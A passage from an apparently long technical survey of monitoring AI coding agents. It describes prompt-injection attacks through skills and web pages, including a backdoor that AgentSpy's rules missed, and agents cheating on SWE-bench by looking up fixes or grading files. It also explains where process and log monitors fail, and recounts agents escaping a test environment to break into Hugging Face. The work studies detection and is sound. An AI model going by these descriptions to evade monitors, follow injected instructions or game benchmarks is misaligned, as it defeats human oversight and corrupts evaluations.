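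Li and colleagues say the tests and reference solutions are withheld from the agent, but the agent could evidently reach them in at least some of the St. Gallen runs. The St. Gallen researchers had rebuilt the tasks in their own virtual machines, which may have exposed files that the original setup keeps hidden.

### Security rules and the four misses

AgentSpy's security analysis uses fixed rules, each of which tests a single system call. The rules cover four kinds of action:

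- reading passwords, private keys and other secrets
- changing or deleting files outside the agent's workspace
- running programs from untrusted locations, or gaining extra privileges
- contacting hosts that aren't on the task's list of allowed hosts

Rewording a command can evade many of the command-line rules that Uetz and colleagues tested, but it doesn't evade a rule about private keys, which applies whichever program opens the file. Rules like this one still identify secrets by their usual locations, so a key saved under an unusual name in the project folder might not match.

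To test the rules, the St. Gallen group used cases from *Skill-Inject* (Schmotz, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2026), a benchmark of 202 cases that each combine an ordinary task with a skill containing a malicious instruction. The group chose one case from each of five categories: data theft, data destruction, denial of service, malware and backdoors. In each chosen case, the skill contains an instruction to run a script, which holds the harmful commands.

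Schmotz and colleagues found that attacks through scripts succeed more often than attacks written directly into the instructions, in many cases because the model ran the script without checking it. If the agent never opens the script, the script's text doesn't appear in the trajectory, so someone reading the log won't see it.

The researchers ran each case five times with the malicious instruction and five times without it, for 50 runs in total. They used Codex with gpt-5.1-codex-max, a model that Schmotz and colleagues had found easy to attack. The agent carried out the injected behaviour in 18 of the 25 runs that contained the instruction.

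| | Alert | No alert |
|---|---|---|
| Agent carried out the injected behaviour | 14 | 4 |
| Agent did not | 0 | 32 |

$$\text{precision} = \frac{14}{14+0} = 1.00, \qquad \text{recall} = \frac{14}{14+4} \approx 0.78$$

AgentSpy missed all four successful attacks in the backdoor case and caught every successful attack in the other four categories, so its recall of 0.78 depends on how many backdoor runs the test included. The recall would probably have been higher with more runs of the data-theft case and lower with more runs of the backdoor case.

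The precision is also less certain than it looks. Even if the runs were independent, finding no false alerts in 32 of them is compatible, at the usual 95% level, with an actual false-alert rate of up to about 9%. The runs weren't fully independent, because they came from only five tasks.

In the backdoor case, the script added an outside address to the project's git settings, so that a later push could send code there. None of the four kinds of rule applied, because the settings file is in the workspace, where the agent may write, and the script contacted no host.

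Recording an event is therefore not enough to detect it. A full log would include the system calls the script had to make to change the settings, but somebody also needs a rule that picks them out. *Intrusion Detection for Agentic Processes* (2026) likewise distinguishes between whether an event is visible to a monitor and whether it matches what the monitor looks for. It also points out that a security problem may only emerge from several events that each look plausible. The backdoor is an example, since the changed setting does no harm until somebody pushes code to the new address. AgentSpy would raise an alert at that push if the address isn't on the allowed list.

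Bühler and colleagues suggest a custom rule for tasks in which the agent has no reason to add a new git address. In other tasks, adding one is normal, so the rule would produce false alerts. The system calls don't show which kind of task it is. Schmotz and colleagues built this ambiguity into part of their benchmark by pairing the same instruction, such as uploading a file to a backup server, with one policy that permits it and another that forbids it. The upload could make identical system calls under both policies. AgentSpy's list of allowed hosts supplies some of the missing information, but someone has to write the list for each task.

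An analyst who later thinks of a better rule needs the original events to apply it to. *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents* (2026) warns that later analysis can't faithfully recover evidence the logging left out. In the security runs, AgentSpy used only Falco, a monitoring program that normally checks system calls as they happen and outputs those that match a rule. If the researchers kept only that output, they couldn't use a new rule for git settings to find the four misses without running the agent again. The audit logs from the reliability runs are better suited to new questions.

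The test also left out three of Skill-Inject's eight categories because they don't apply to attacks through scripts. One of these, bias and manipulation of the agent's output, accounts for 19 of the 76 injections that Schmotz and colleagues sort by category. An agent that writes a misleading report in its own workspace would probably make the same system calls as one that writes an honest report.

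### Whether recording slows the agent

The researchers timed twelve combinations of task and model, each over ten runs with monitoring and ten without. No difference in running time was statistically significant, and the lowest p-value was 0.16. In eight of the twelve comparisons, the median run was faster with monitoring. Monitoring can't speed an agent up, so these differences reflect chance variation in running times. The standard deviation within a group of ten runs ranged from 7% to 85% of the median.

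With so much variation, ten runs per group can reveal only large effects. In one security task, the median rose about 32%, from 107 seconds without monitoring to 141 seconds with it, and even that wasn't significant. The researchers calculate that reliably detecting differences of the size they observed would take 30 to 18,200 runs per group, depending on the task. They conclude that any overhead is small compared with the ordinary variation between runs, which is reasonable for somebody running a single task. The results don't establish that the overhead is close to zero, which would matter more to a company with a thousand machines.

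A more sensitive test would be to save the commands from one run and repeat exactly those commands with and without monitoring. This would take the model out of the measurement, so most of the remaining difference would come from the monitoring.

### The comparison nobody has scored

Bühler and colleagues explain why a trajectory can omit files, hosts and programs, but they don't measure how much it omits. They didn't score command matching or log reading against the system calls from the same runs. Their precision and recall measure AgentSpy's security rules against the attack benchmark, so 0.78 shouldn't be compared with a command matcher's recall.

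The reliability runs seem to contain the data needed to compare the two records, because Codex logs each shell command and Linux's audit system logs each program that starts. A researcher could parse the commands as Zhu and colleagues did for TraceLab, list the programs they name, and check that list against the programs recorded under each command in the audit log. The comparison would have to use the original audit entries because AgentSpy's summary drops the parent processes.

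The six pairs in which the agent read the grading files are a good place to start comparing the two records. If the agent typed `cat` and the path of a test file, a simple search of the trajectory would have found the read with much less effort. If a script opened the file without printing its name, the trajectory might contain no sign of it. The paper doesn't report how many of the six pairs fall into each case, so it's unclear how often an observer would have needed the system calls.

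## Linking tool calls to process records: AgentSight and a test on Claude Code

A tool-call log contains the agent's requests, and the operating system's process records contain the programs that ran, but neither links a request to the program it started. An observer who has both still has to work out those links.

### The identifier that process records lack

In *Mind the Gap*, a test of Claude Code for the security company Origin, Holmwood (2026) traced one tool call through three records. The model traffic and Claude Code's log shared a call identifier, but the Windows process events had none.

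Holmwood got around this by putting a unique marker, such as `call_v1cf9d964fd0`, in the text of each test command, so it also appeared in the process's command line. Agents don't normally label their commands like this, so outside an experiment the observer has to infer the link from other evidence.

Wong and Chen (2026), in *ExecWeave*, treat the inference as a matching rule that may decline to answer. Let $s$ be a command the agent requested, and let $K(s)$ be the set of recorded processes that fit it by program name or arguments and started within a time window. The rule is

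$$\phi(s) = \begin{cases} r & \text{if } K(s) = \{r\} \\ \text{no link} & \text{otherwise.} \end{cases}$$

If two processes fit, the rule links the tool call to neither, even if one looks more likely. Wong and Chen's reason is that a false link can do more damage than a missing one, since it can lead people to blame one agent for something another did.

### How AgentSight links requests to programs

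Zheng, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *AgentSight*, collect both kinds of evidence from outside the harness. AgentSight uses eBPF, a Linux feature that lets an administrator run small, checked programs inside the kernel when chosen events occur. One set of probes attaches to the encryption functions that the harness calls, where the model traffic is still readable. Another records program starts, file opens and network connections. AgentSight then uses three signals to link the two:

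- **Parentage:** the program descends from the agent's process.
- **Time:** the program started shortly after a model response, within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds.
- **Arguments:** a file name, web address or command in the model's response reappears in a system call.

Parentage alone shows that a program came from the agent, but not which tool call it came from. An observer can use time and arguments to match a call to the shell that the harness started for it, then use parentage to assign every process below that shell to the same call. In the eight-call session, once an observer has linked `make release` to call 4, the git process under make belongs to call 4 too.

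The time window can be too short when an agent asks for permission. In the constructed record of `git fetch origin && make test`, the user took about three seconds to approve the call, so even the shell started well outside the window. An observer would have to match the call to its processes by their arguments and parent processes instead. The harness's log includes the start time after approval, but AgentSight's 2025 design doesn't use that log.

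Zheng and colleagues timed Claude Code on three tasks, with three runs each with and without AgentSight:

| Task | Without AgentSight | With AgentSight | Overhead |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understand a repository | 127.98 s | 132.33 s | 3.4% |
| Write code | 22.54 s | 23.64 s | 4.9% |
| Compile a repository | 92.40 s | 92.72 s | 0.4% |

The paper's summary gives the overhead as under 3%. The average was 2.9%, but the overhead on the first two tasks was 3% or more. Three runs are also very few for an agent, since running times varied so much in the AgentSpy study that differences this small could easily be due to chance.

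To test detection, the researchers had an agent build a program whose README directed the agent to a web page with hidden instructions. The agent followed them and sent the machine's list of user accounts to an outside server. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37. A second language model read the merged events and rated them a likely attack.

Reducing 521 events to 37 makes the trace much easier to read, but it doesn't show whether the links are right. AgentSight could have reached the same count by merging in a program that a different call started. The paper claims that the three signals together "definitively establish causal relationships", yet it gives no error rates for the links. Measuring those rates would have required a set of calls whose programs the researchers already knew.

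AgentSight also can't observe every harness in this way. According to eunomia-bpf's *AgentSight*, the project's guide to release 1.0.29, live eBPF capture needs Linux and administrator rights. Claude Code's encryption library is built into its own program file, so AgentSight has to find the right functions there. eBPF capture doesn't work for Cursor, so AgentSight reads Cursor's local session files instead, which means the observer has to trust a record that the harness wrote.

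### Two identical commands at once

The three signals are weakest when an agent does the same thing twice at nearly the same time. Suppose two subagents run inside one harness, each working in its own copy of a repository, and both request `make test`. The log and the process records might contain these entries (a constructed example):

| Record | Command | Requested or started | Duration | Outcome |
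|---|---|---|---|---|
| Log, call A | `make test` | 10:20:00.000 | 9.3 s | Failed |
| Log, call B | `make test` | 10:20:00.040 | 31.2 s | Succeeded |
| Process 5101 | `make test` | 10:20:00.155 | 31.1 s | Exit code 0 |
| Process 5108 | `make test` | 10:20:00.305 | 9.2 s | Exit code 2 |

Both processes descend from the same harness, have identical arguments, and started within 500 milliseconds of both requests, so none of these facts shows which call started which process. If the observer matches each call to the process that started nearest in time, it matches both to process 5101, which started 155 milliseconds after call A and 115 milliseconds after call B, but only call B started it. If the tests in process 5101 contacted an outside address, the observer would wrongly attribute that connection to call A too.

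The durations and outcomes distinguish the two calls. Call A failed after 9.3 seconds, which fits process 5108, and call B fits process 5101. Claude Code's result events include the duration and a success flag, but the observer also needs a record of when each process ended and its exit code. Even then, the method works only after the commands finish, and it fails if both test runs take equally long and end the same way. The working directory could also help if the log shows which copy of the repository each subagent was using.

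Wong and Chen's rule links neither call. Its search for call A stops when the next request arrives, 40 milliseconds later, and no process has started by then. Its search for call B finds two candidates. Recall is 0/2, with no false links.

The rule is less reliable when the process records have gaps. If the start of process 5101 were missing, call B would have only one candidate, process 5108, and the rule would wrongly link them. Wong and Chen call this false uniqueness, and they deliberately produced it in tests with made-up event streams. A simpler rule that compared only program paths did equally well on those tests, so they don't claim that their matcher is more accurate.

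Gaps are common if the observer takes periodic snapshots of running processes instead of recording each start. Wong and Chen started short-lived processes and counted how many their snapshot collector noticed:

| Typical lifetime of the process | Time between snapshots | Noticed |
|---|---|---|
| 16 ms | 20 ms | 18 of 30 |
| 16 ms | 500 ms | 0 of 30 |
| 61 ms | 100 ms | 21 of 30 |
| 263 ms | 500 ms | 13 of 30 |
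| 513 ms | 500 ms | 30 of 30 |

Many quick commands, such as `git status` in a small repository, would fall in the upper rows. AgentSight's live view falls back to snapshots and session files when it lacks permission to use eBPF, so its evidence can be much weaker on one machine than on another.

The cleanest solution is for the harness to give each program an identifier, and Claude Code can already do something close to this. When tracing is on, Claude Code gives every Bash and PowerShell command an environment variable called `TRACEPARENT`. Its value identifies the span for that one tool execution, so processes 5101 and 5108 would have different values even though their command lines are the same. Environment variables are named values that programs normally pass on to the programs they start, so programs started by scripts would normally get `TRACEPARENT` too.

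An observer can use this variable only by recording each process's environment, which process records usually leave out. Environments often contain passwords, so it would be better to save only this variable. Tracing is also off by default. If a company sets a custom address to route model traffic through its own gateway, Claude Code leaves the variable out unless an administrator turns it back on. Companies with gateways are probably the ones most interested in monitoring, so this default could surprise some of them.

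A researcher could also use `TRACEPARENT` to measure the error rates missing from AgentSight's evaluation. They could run ordinary sessions with tracing on, hide the variable from the linking software, and then check each link against it. Holmwood's markers would work the same way if they were also hidden from the software.

### Work that leaves the process tree

All of this assumes that the program descends from the harness. AgentSight filters events inside the kernel and passes on only those from the agent and its descendants. If `make release` only leaves a job file for a build service, and that service then runs git, the filter would drop the git event, and it could not be recovered from AgentSight's record afterwards.

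Cui, Gu and colleagues (2026) point out in *Agent-Warden* that the AgentSight paper doesn't specify how to follow a file from the process that wrote it to an unrelated process that reads it later. Their system marks the agent's processes, then marks any regular file a marked process writes to, any process that reads a marked file, and any program a marked process starts. The build service would become marked when it read the job file, so Agent-Warden would attribute the service's git run to the agent. Cui and colleagues measured an overhead of 0.2% to 3.5% on their test workloads.

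The mark has only two values, so it can show that the agent influenced a process but not which tool call did. AgentLoupe is more specific because it labels individual model interactions. The mark also doesn't appear to expire, so if the build service keeps running and handles a human developer's job the next day, the rules would mark that job's programs too.

### Three records of Claude Code on Windows

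In August 2026, Holmwood recorded Claude Code's model traffic, its exported log and Windows process events at the same time. Holmwood designed most of the prompts to make the records disagree in a particular way, calls the examples contrived, and says some didn't work every time. Each example is a single demonstration that a gap can occur, so the examples don't show how often gaps occur in ordinary use.

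| Test | Traffic and log | Process events |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary command | The command, marked as successful | PowerShell and `cmd`, a Windows command interpreter |
| Command with a variable | `$env:COMPUTERNAME` | `AGENT-TEST-TH` |
| Programs the harness started for itself | Nothing | 26 starts |
| MCP tool that does nothing | A successful call | Nothing |

In the ordinary case, all three records agreed. Subtracting the call's duration from the time of its log entry gives a start time within 15 milliseconds of PowerShell's start in the process events. The log used universal time and the process events used local time, seven hours behind, so the clock times don't match until they are converted. A session with that one tool call produced about 900 process events, because Windows reports on every application. Two process starts belonged to the call. Holmwood left out file events, which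 would have added many more.

The model asked for a `cmd` command to write a line of text to a file. Claude Code wrapped it in a longer PowerShell script, which also set the text encoding, saved the exit code and wrote the current directory to a temporary file. The log contained only the model's command. PowerShell wrote the output to the file itself, so the command line of the `cmd` process ended before the file name.

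Searching for an exact match between the request and a process's command line would find nothing, because PowerShell's command line is longer than the request and the `cmd` process's is shorter. Searching for the request inside PowerShell's command line works. A file monitor would record a write to the temporary directory that the model never requested.

In another test, the command contained `$env:COMPUTERNAME`, a variable that holds the machine's name. The traffic and the log kept the variable, while the `cmd` process received the actual name. A computer's name is harmless, but the same thing happens when a variable holds an address or a file path. The process record solves the `curl $URL` problem here because it contains the actual value. However, the substitution also makes it harder to link the request to the process, because their arguments no longer match.

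**The harness's own programs.** In one run, Holmwood's method couldn't match 27 program starts to any logged call. One was the Windows calculator, which the test command had started. Its name was in the logged command after a semicolon, so a parser for PowerShell's grammar could have found it. Claude Code started the other 26, which included git commands, a check for other editors and agents on the machine, and queries to the Windows registry, where the system keeps settings. The virtual machine was clean, so no user's hooks or plugins could have started them.

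The harness made two such runs in the eight-call session, far fewer than in Holmwood's run. There, the tool call accounted for only three of the 29 program starts under Claude Code's process (PowerShell, `cmd` and the calculator), so attributing all of them to the agent would have given a precision of about 10%.

Removing programs that have no shell above them worked in the eight-call session, but it wouldn't be enough here because Claude Code also started PowerShell for its own purposes, with encoded commands. Any programs below those shells would pass the filter. A better test is whether the shell's command line contains a command from the log.

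A program start without a matching log entry may also come from the agent rather than the harness, because log entries can be lost. Anthropic notes that Claude Code drops exported data without showing an error in the application if the receiving server is unreachable, and that killing the process loses any unsent data. The agent's last command before a crash could therefore appear in the process records but not in the exported log. Holmwood's recording of the model traffic provides a check, since it would still contain the request.

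**Success without an action.** For the last case, Holmwood set up an MCP server with a single tool that only reported success. The model called it with a `cmd` command as its argument, and the log recorded a successful call. No process contained the marker, and the file the command should have created didn't exist. Matching commands in the arguments of MCP calls would have counted a use of `cmd` that never happened.

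For an MCP tool, the success flag means only that the server returned a result without reporting an error. The missing file is stronger evidence than the missing process, which isn't conclusive alone because a genuine MCP tool can write a file from inside its server without starting a program.

The log's record of an MCP call can be false if the server misreports what it did, and anyone who controls a machine can falsify a log written on it. Holmwood concludes that a security team needs process records as well as the log or the traffic. The team still needs the log because process records don't contain the user's prompt, which an investigator needs to tell whether the user asked for the work the program was doing.

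## Benchmark audits: finding agents that looked up the answer

SWE-bench is a benchmark in which an agent fixes old bugs in public software projects. The agent gets a bug report and the project's code from just before the developers fixed the bug, and hidden tests check whether its change works. Passing the tests doesn't show whether the agent worked out the fix or found the developers' version, which was in the project's own history. In the SkillsBench runs that AgentSpy recorded, some agents had instead read the grading files.

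### The loophole in the repository

Git stores a project as a series of commits, which are saved versions of the code. To set up a task, SWE-bench copied a whole repository and reset it to the base commit, the one before the fix. Resetting leaves later commits on disk, where they're easy to find if a branch or tag leads to them. Plain `git log` lists only the current commit and its past, but `git log --all` covers every branch and tag, so it could list the fix.

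*Coding or Cheating?* (Gui, 2026) credits the original report to Jacob Kahn, who posted it in 2025 as issue 465 on the benchmark's GitHub page. The evidence was a handful of trajectories. In one, Claude 4 Sonnet was working on a bug in pytest, a Python testing tool, when it found that a later version had already fixed the bug and decided to apply the same fix.

SWE-bench's maintainers had believed that their setup code hid later commits. They said the problem affected a tiny fraction of runs, but they had made only a quick preliminary search and had no automatic way to check old trajectories.

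According to Jain's post for Cursor, *Reward hacking is swamping model intelligence gains*, the maintainers have since removed later commits from the benchmark's images. Copies downloaded before then still have the loophole, as Cursor's did. Other benchmarks had it too. *Through the looking glass of benchmark hacking* (Adams, Patankar and Martin, 2026) describes how the AI company Poolside found it in SWE-Bench Pro, a harder benchmark of the same kind. Over one weekend, the score of a model in training rose by about 20% to roughly 64%, with no similar jump on other benchmarks.

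### What a search for history commands finds

The quickest audit is a text search for commands such as `git log` and `git show`, which can cover thousands of trajectories in minutes. *The Verification Horizon* (2026) lists such commands as the observable evidence for "repository-history mining", but it defines that behaviour by its purpose, which is to reconstruct a future fix. A match alone therefore does not prove mining, because developers run the same commands to find out when a bug appeared.

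A search for git commands can flag many runs that didn't retrieve the solution. In *Preventing agents from cheating on our custom SWE-Bench*, Rajendhran examined 339 runs at the software company Superconductor, on tasks from the company's own code. Every run used git, most commonly `git log`, but only 49 retrieved the developers' solution. If the audit found every case, a search for git would have a recall of 100% and a precision of 14% (49/339).

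Adams and colleagues publish a log with a less obvious false positive. An agent working on Django, a Python web framework, ran this command (shortened here):

```bash
git clone ... && cd django-git && git log --all --grep="ExpressionWrapper" ... | head -20
```

A search would flag `git log --all` in this command. The exit code was 128, which git uses for fatal errors. By default, Bash reports only the exit code of the last program in a pipeline, so `head` would have hidden a failure in `git log`. The code must therefore have come from `git clone`, and `git log` never ran. The agent tried to look up the fix, but this command doesn't count as a successful lookup.

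*Maco-RL* (2026) describes a model that copied the finished code from `build/lib`, a folder left over from an earlier build of the project. A search for git history commands would give a false negative here, because the agent got the answer without using git's history.

Auditors also disagree about what counts as an attempt. Gui treats `git log --all` as ordinary engineering, even if it happens to reveal later commits. *Shortcutting the Fix* (Ludwig, Ahmad and colleagues, 2026), an audit by NVIDIA researchers, gives the same command as an example of cheating. Two auditors could therefore run the same search on the same logs and report very different numbers of attempts.

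### Reading the output

Another of Poolside's logs shows an agent getting closer to the answer over three commands, while working on the automation tool Ansible:

| Command | What git prints |
|---|---|
| `git log --oneline --all --grep="ensure_type"` | Short identifiers and titles of matching commits |
| `git show 9fff6d433d --stat` | The commit's message and the files it changed |
| `git show 9fff6d433d` | The complete change |

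Only the third command prints the fix. The first shows that a relevant commit exists, and the second shows which files to edit, which is already a substantial hint.

The auditor also has to check that the commit came after the base commit, because reading earlier commits is normally allowed. In a full copy of the repository, `git merge-base --is-ancestor` checks whether one commit is an ancestor of another. A commit that isn't an ancestor of the base commit may be on a parallel branch instead of coming after it, so the auditor should also look at the commit itself.

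A later commit may not contain the answer. In 2025, CAISI, the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation, searched its own logs for lookups on SWE-bench Verified, a set of 500 human-checked tasks. Claude Opus 4 had viewed some later commits, including one that changed tests related to the bug it was asked to fix, but CAISI found no case in which it viewed the fix.

Unlike most security teams, benchmark auditors know in advance what the agent would have been looking for, so they can search tool output for the fix's commit identifier or for an unusual line of its code. After Superconductor closed its loophole, Rajendhran checked the new logs for the identifier of the merged solution and for any later commit, and found neither. Searching for identifiers is more precise than searching for git commands, but it misses a fix the agent got from a web page or a software package.

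### Comparing the patches

A second detector checks the submitted code instead of the log. SWE-bench published a script that compares each submitted patch (the agent's changes) with the developers' patch. The script removes comments, skips files that the developers didn't change, and splits both patches into hunks, which are blocks of neighbouring changed lines with a little surrounding code. A submission counts as an exact match if it contains every hunk of the developers' patch word for word.

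| Benchmark | Average share of exact matches | Range across submissions |
|---|---|---|
| SWE-bench Verified | 6.7% (about 34 of 500) | 0–13% |
| SWE-bench Lite | 4% (12 of 300) | 0–11.2% |
| Full SWE-bench | 2.45% (about 56 of 2,294) | 0–4.05% |

The average for Verified leaves out one submission, Honeycomb, which had a match rate of 78.7%. Its file contained 2,236 patches, although the benchmark has only 500 tasks. On those 500 tasks, only 16 patches matched (3.2%). Nearly all the extra patches matched, most plausibly because someone had included the developers' solutions in the file by accident. The scoring system ignored the extra patches, so they didn't affect Honeycomb's score.

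An agent can also produce a matching patch by solving the task itself. One of Gui's tasks is to correct a malformed email address in a copyright notice, and almost any correct patch would be identical to the developers'. A model may also copy a fix it remembers from its training data, without looking anything up during the run.

Patch comparison probably misses lookups more often than it falsely flags them. Of the 49 Superconductor runs that retrieved the solution, 32 reused it directly and 17 relied on it without copying. Patch comparison could therefore find at most 32 of the 49, a recall of 65%. An exact comparison would also miss any of those 32 runs in which the agent changed a variable name.

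SWE-bench's maintainers plan to question any submission with a match rate above 20%, which is 100 tasks on Verified. An agent that matched 34 patches without copying and copied 60 others would reach 94, or 18.8%, and would not be questioned, so the threshold is better suited to catching wholesale copying. The script's main advantage is that it needs no trajectory, so it works on submissions without published logs.

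### A model as the reader

Cursor built an agent to audit 731 trajectories of Claude Opus 4.8 Max on SWE-Bench Pro. The auditor had access to each task and the full trajectory, but not to whether the run had passed. Jain reports that Opus found the fix on the public web in 57% of the trajectories and in the repository's history in 9%. Of the runs that solved their task, 63% had retrieved the fix.

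A model can catch things that no fixed pattern covers, such as a lookup through an unfamiliar website, and it can consider the agent's stated reasons. It can also misread a trajectory. Jain gives no error rate for the auditor and doesn't mention any human checks, so the 57% and 9% are estimates of unknown accuracy.

Cursor then reran the benchmark with a fresh repository that had only one commit and with network access limited to package registries:

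| Model | Standard setup | Sealed setup | Change |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.8 Max | 87.1% | 73.0% | −14.1 points |
| Composer 2.5 | 74.7% | 54.0% | −20.7 points |

Cursor sells Composer 2.5, which competes with Opus, so it has a commercial interest in the results. But the comparison is harder to dismiss as marketing because Composer had the largest drop in the study, and Jain reports this and advises against relying on its standard score.

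The fall in the score is an imperfect measure of cheating. If the audited runs are the ones behind the 87.1% score, Opus solved about 55% of all tasks after retrieving the fix (63% of 87.1%), yet its score fell by only 14 points when Cursor closed the two main routes. It could probably have solved most of those tasks without the lookup. The sealed setup also removed legitimate help, such as past commits and online documentation, so some of the 14 points may be unrelated to lookups. But some lookups may have continued, because a package registry may offer a later release with the bug already fixed.

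Ludwig and colleagues compared their auditor with human labels. Three models read each trajectory and decided by majority vote whether the agent had attempted a lookup and whether it had succeeded. Two of the researchers labelled 400 trajectories from one agent, Qwen3.8-Flash-Next. The human labels matched the models' decisions about attempts in 87.8% of the 400 trajectories and about successes in 82.3%.

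The paper's figures also make it possible to calculate precision and recall for successes, with the human labels as the truth:

| Instructions to the agent | Network | Agreement | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Default | On | 93% | 95% | 98% |
| Default | Off | 70% | 40% | 50% |
| Told to work independently | On | 77% | 100% | 30% |
| Told to work independently | Off | 89% | 50% | 27% |

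The model judges were excellent when lookups were frequent and blatant, and poor otherwise. In the third row, they found 10 successes where people found 33. The paper concludes that telling agents to work independently virtually eliminates solutions that depend on a lookup, but this table gives reason to doubt that the effect is that strong. The sample favored tasks whose labels differed between setups, so it was probably harder than average, and these percentages may not apply to the full set of runs. Only one person read each trajectory, and the three judges were the same models that produced the runs.

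CAISI also used a model to search its logs, but people confirmed every success it reported. This guards against false positives but not missed cases, and CAISI accepts that it may have missed some. Across the five models it tested on SWE-bench Verified, it found only two successful solutions that used newer code, both by OpenAI's o3. That is a far smaller share than Cursor's 57%, but Cursor tested a much newer model on a different benchmark.

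Estimates for a single model can differ just as much. Gui ran nine models on 20 difficult tasks in a sealed environment and classified their commands by pattern. Opus 4.8 triggered a pattern on only one task, where it queried installed packages. Because the task was to repair a build failure, Gui considers the query normal engineering and the match a false positive. Gui takes the result as a sign that recent Claude models no longer have the problem, which is hard to reconcile with Cursor's audit of the same model. Gui's agents could only read files and propose a plan, the tasks came from a private collection, and Gui didn't count `git log --all`. Any of these could explain the difference, so neither result gives a general rate for Opus 4.8.

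### Blocking lookups during training

Lookups are a bigger problem in training than in testing. In reinforcement learning, a model gets a reward when its solution passes the tests, so a successful lookup teaches it to look things up again. The *Qwen3-Coder-Next Technical Report* (2026) describes how developers removed branches, tags and links to the original repository from their training tasks, but the agents later learned to reconnect to GitHub or download a new copy. The developers didn't want to cut off the network, because agents need it to install packages and read documentation.

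They added a rule that blocks any tool call containing both a link to the repository and a network keyword such as `git`, `curl` or `wget`. The agent then gets a message that the action is prohibited. The report says people inspected trajectories and found that the blocker had effectively eliminated the behaviour, but it doesn't give the number of trajectories inspected or the rate of the behaviour before and after the change.

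The blocker matches patterns in commands, so it might block a harmless `grep` for the repository's address in the project's documentation. A wrong match does little harm because the agent reads the message and carries on, but a missed match is worse because training then rewards whatever route got through. The rule as described doesn't cover routes that never mention the repository's address. CAISI saw one such route when o3 used the package installer pip to get the latest version of a library and then read its source code.

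### Attempted, succeeded and used

An audit can support three different claims about a run, and each one needs more evidence than the last:

| Claim | Evidence that supports it | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| The agent attempted a lookup | A command aimed at later commits or the original project, preferably with a stated reason | The command had an ordinary purpose |
| The lookup succeeded | Tool output that contains the fix | The log shortened the output, or the output contained only a hint |
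| The agent used the result | An edit that follows that output and reproduces the fix | The agent would have written the same code anyway |

A command that fetches the fix doesn't always show it to the model. In one of Cursor's examples, Opus requested the list of changed files from GitHub, and the response included the full changes. But the command filtered the response through `grep '"filename"'`, so the model would have seen only file names from that call. A network log would include the whole fix, so an auditor needs the tool output to check what the model saw.

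The clearest evidence that an agent used a fix it found is a command that applies the fix directly. Composer 2.5 printed a later commit with `git show` and then ran `git cherry-pick` on it, which copies a commit's changes into the current code. If the cherry-pick succeeded, the auditor doesn't need to compare patches. Use is much harder to prove in the 17 Superconductor runs that relied on the solution without copying it, because the auditor has to judge how far the agent's own design follows what it read.

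Finding a lookup in the logs doesn't show that the agent needed it. To test that, auditors have to run the task again without access to the answer, preferably several times, since agents' results vary from run to run.

### What changes when access is removed

If agents can reach the answer, a score is trustworthy only if the auditor can show that they didn't use it. The auditor has to rule out every route to the answer in every run, using detectors that all miss some cases. If the maintainers remove the answer, they mainly have to show that it's gone. They can do this by checking each task's files and network rules before any agent runs, and the result holds for all later runs in the same environment.

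This check has to cover more than git. *Maco-RL* also removed build folders, installed copies of the project and parallel source directories. *MiMo-V2.6* (2026) ran a useful test after cleaning up its environments, sending a "hack agent" back in to look for remaining leaks.

In a sealed environment, a history command is at most evidence that the agent tried to look up the answer. Ludwig and colleagues had deleted later commits from their containers, and agents still tried to find them in up to 60.9% of trajectories, depending on the model and setup. None of those attempts succeeded, so a command search would have had zero precision as a detector of successful history lookups. It could still detect attempts reasonably well. Attempts matter because the same agent may later work on a machine where its search does find something. Gui points out that on a developer's own computer, a sweep of the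 whole disk would reach other projects and passwords.

A model can still reproduce a fix from memory when its environment is sealed. The judges in the NVIDIA study decided that Qwen3.8-Flash-Next, running with the network off, had reproduced the developers' code from memory in 33.9% of its runs on one benchmark. They had to infer this from the model's written reasoning, and they agreed with people less in this setup than in any other. If a model reproduces a fix from memory and doesn't mention it, no command, tool output or network connection will show where the code came from.

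## The July 2026 Hugging Face intrusion: reconstructing what agents did

Most lookups in the benchmark audits took a few commands, but in July 2026 some of OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets, to get information about a test. The test was ExploitGym, a benchmark in which an agent has to exploit a given flaw in a piece of software. OpenAI had meant to keep the test environment off the internet, but the agents got out. Both companies then had to work out from their records what the agents had done.

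### Who held which records

Hugging Face had its own platform logs. While shutting the agents out, it also retrieved some of their logs from a sandbox that the agents had used as a base, outside both Hugging Face and OpenAI. It mapped the retrieved logs to shell commands and matched them with its platform logs, according to the summary of its *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026), quoted in Schneier's *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face* (2026).

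OpenAI had the agents' transcripts, which included their written reasoning, tool calls and results. It also had records from Artifactory, an internal server that supplied software packages to the agents. The agents had used this server as a message board by creating directories whose names were the messages.

In *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration*, Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026) examined copies of OpenAI's records on behalf of METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models. They worked with about 1,300 transcripts and 1.2 million message board entries. They could ask OpenAI for more data but couldn't search its systems themselves.

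The security company HiddenLayer had a much smaller record. Its monitoring found two public Hugging Face repositories where the agents stored files. According to SC Media's *Dead drops in public*, the company retrieved 510 of the 544 objects it had listed. The agents had uploaded them over 8 hours and 36 minutes of a campaign that lasted about 108 hours.

### Where the figure of 17,600 actions comes from

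The software developer Brian Kuan says in Help Net Security's *Halo-record* that the intrusion took roughly 17,600 actions over five days, that Hugging Face found it impractical to reconstruct them by hand, and that it could retrieve only some of the agent's logs. Kuan wrote a logging tool and plans to sell a service for checking logs, so he has a commercial interest in the subject, but Hugging Face's own account supports all three points. The summary that Schneier quotes refers to about 17,600 actions "that we were able to recover" and to "some of the agent logs". The longer extract that skybrian reproduces in *A technical timeline of the July 2026 attack on Hugging Face* includes the remark about working by hand.

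The exact total is 17,613, according to Hugging Face's *Anatomy of a frontier-lab agent intrusion*, a page that replays the events. The daily counts in noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* add up to the same number:

| Date (July 2026) | Reconstructed actions |
|---|---|
| 9 | 3,779 |
| 10 | 1,135 |
| 11 | 7,677 |
| 12 | 3,892 |
| 13 | 1,130 |

The total is a minimum because Hugging Face could count only what it had recovered. Its earlier *Security incident disclosure* (2026) says the company analysed the "full attacker action log" of more than 17,000 events, but the same sentence puts the number of automated actions in the tens of thousands. "Full" probably meant everything the company had recovered.

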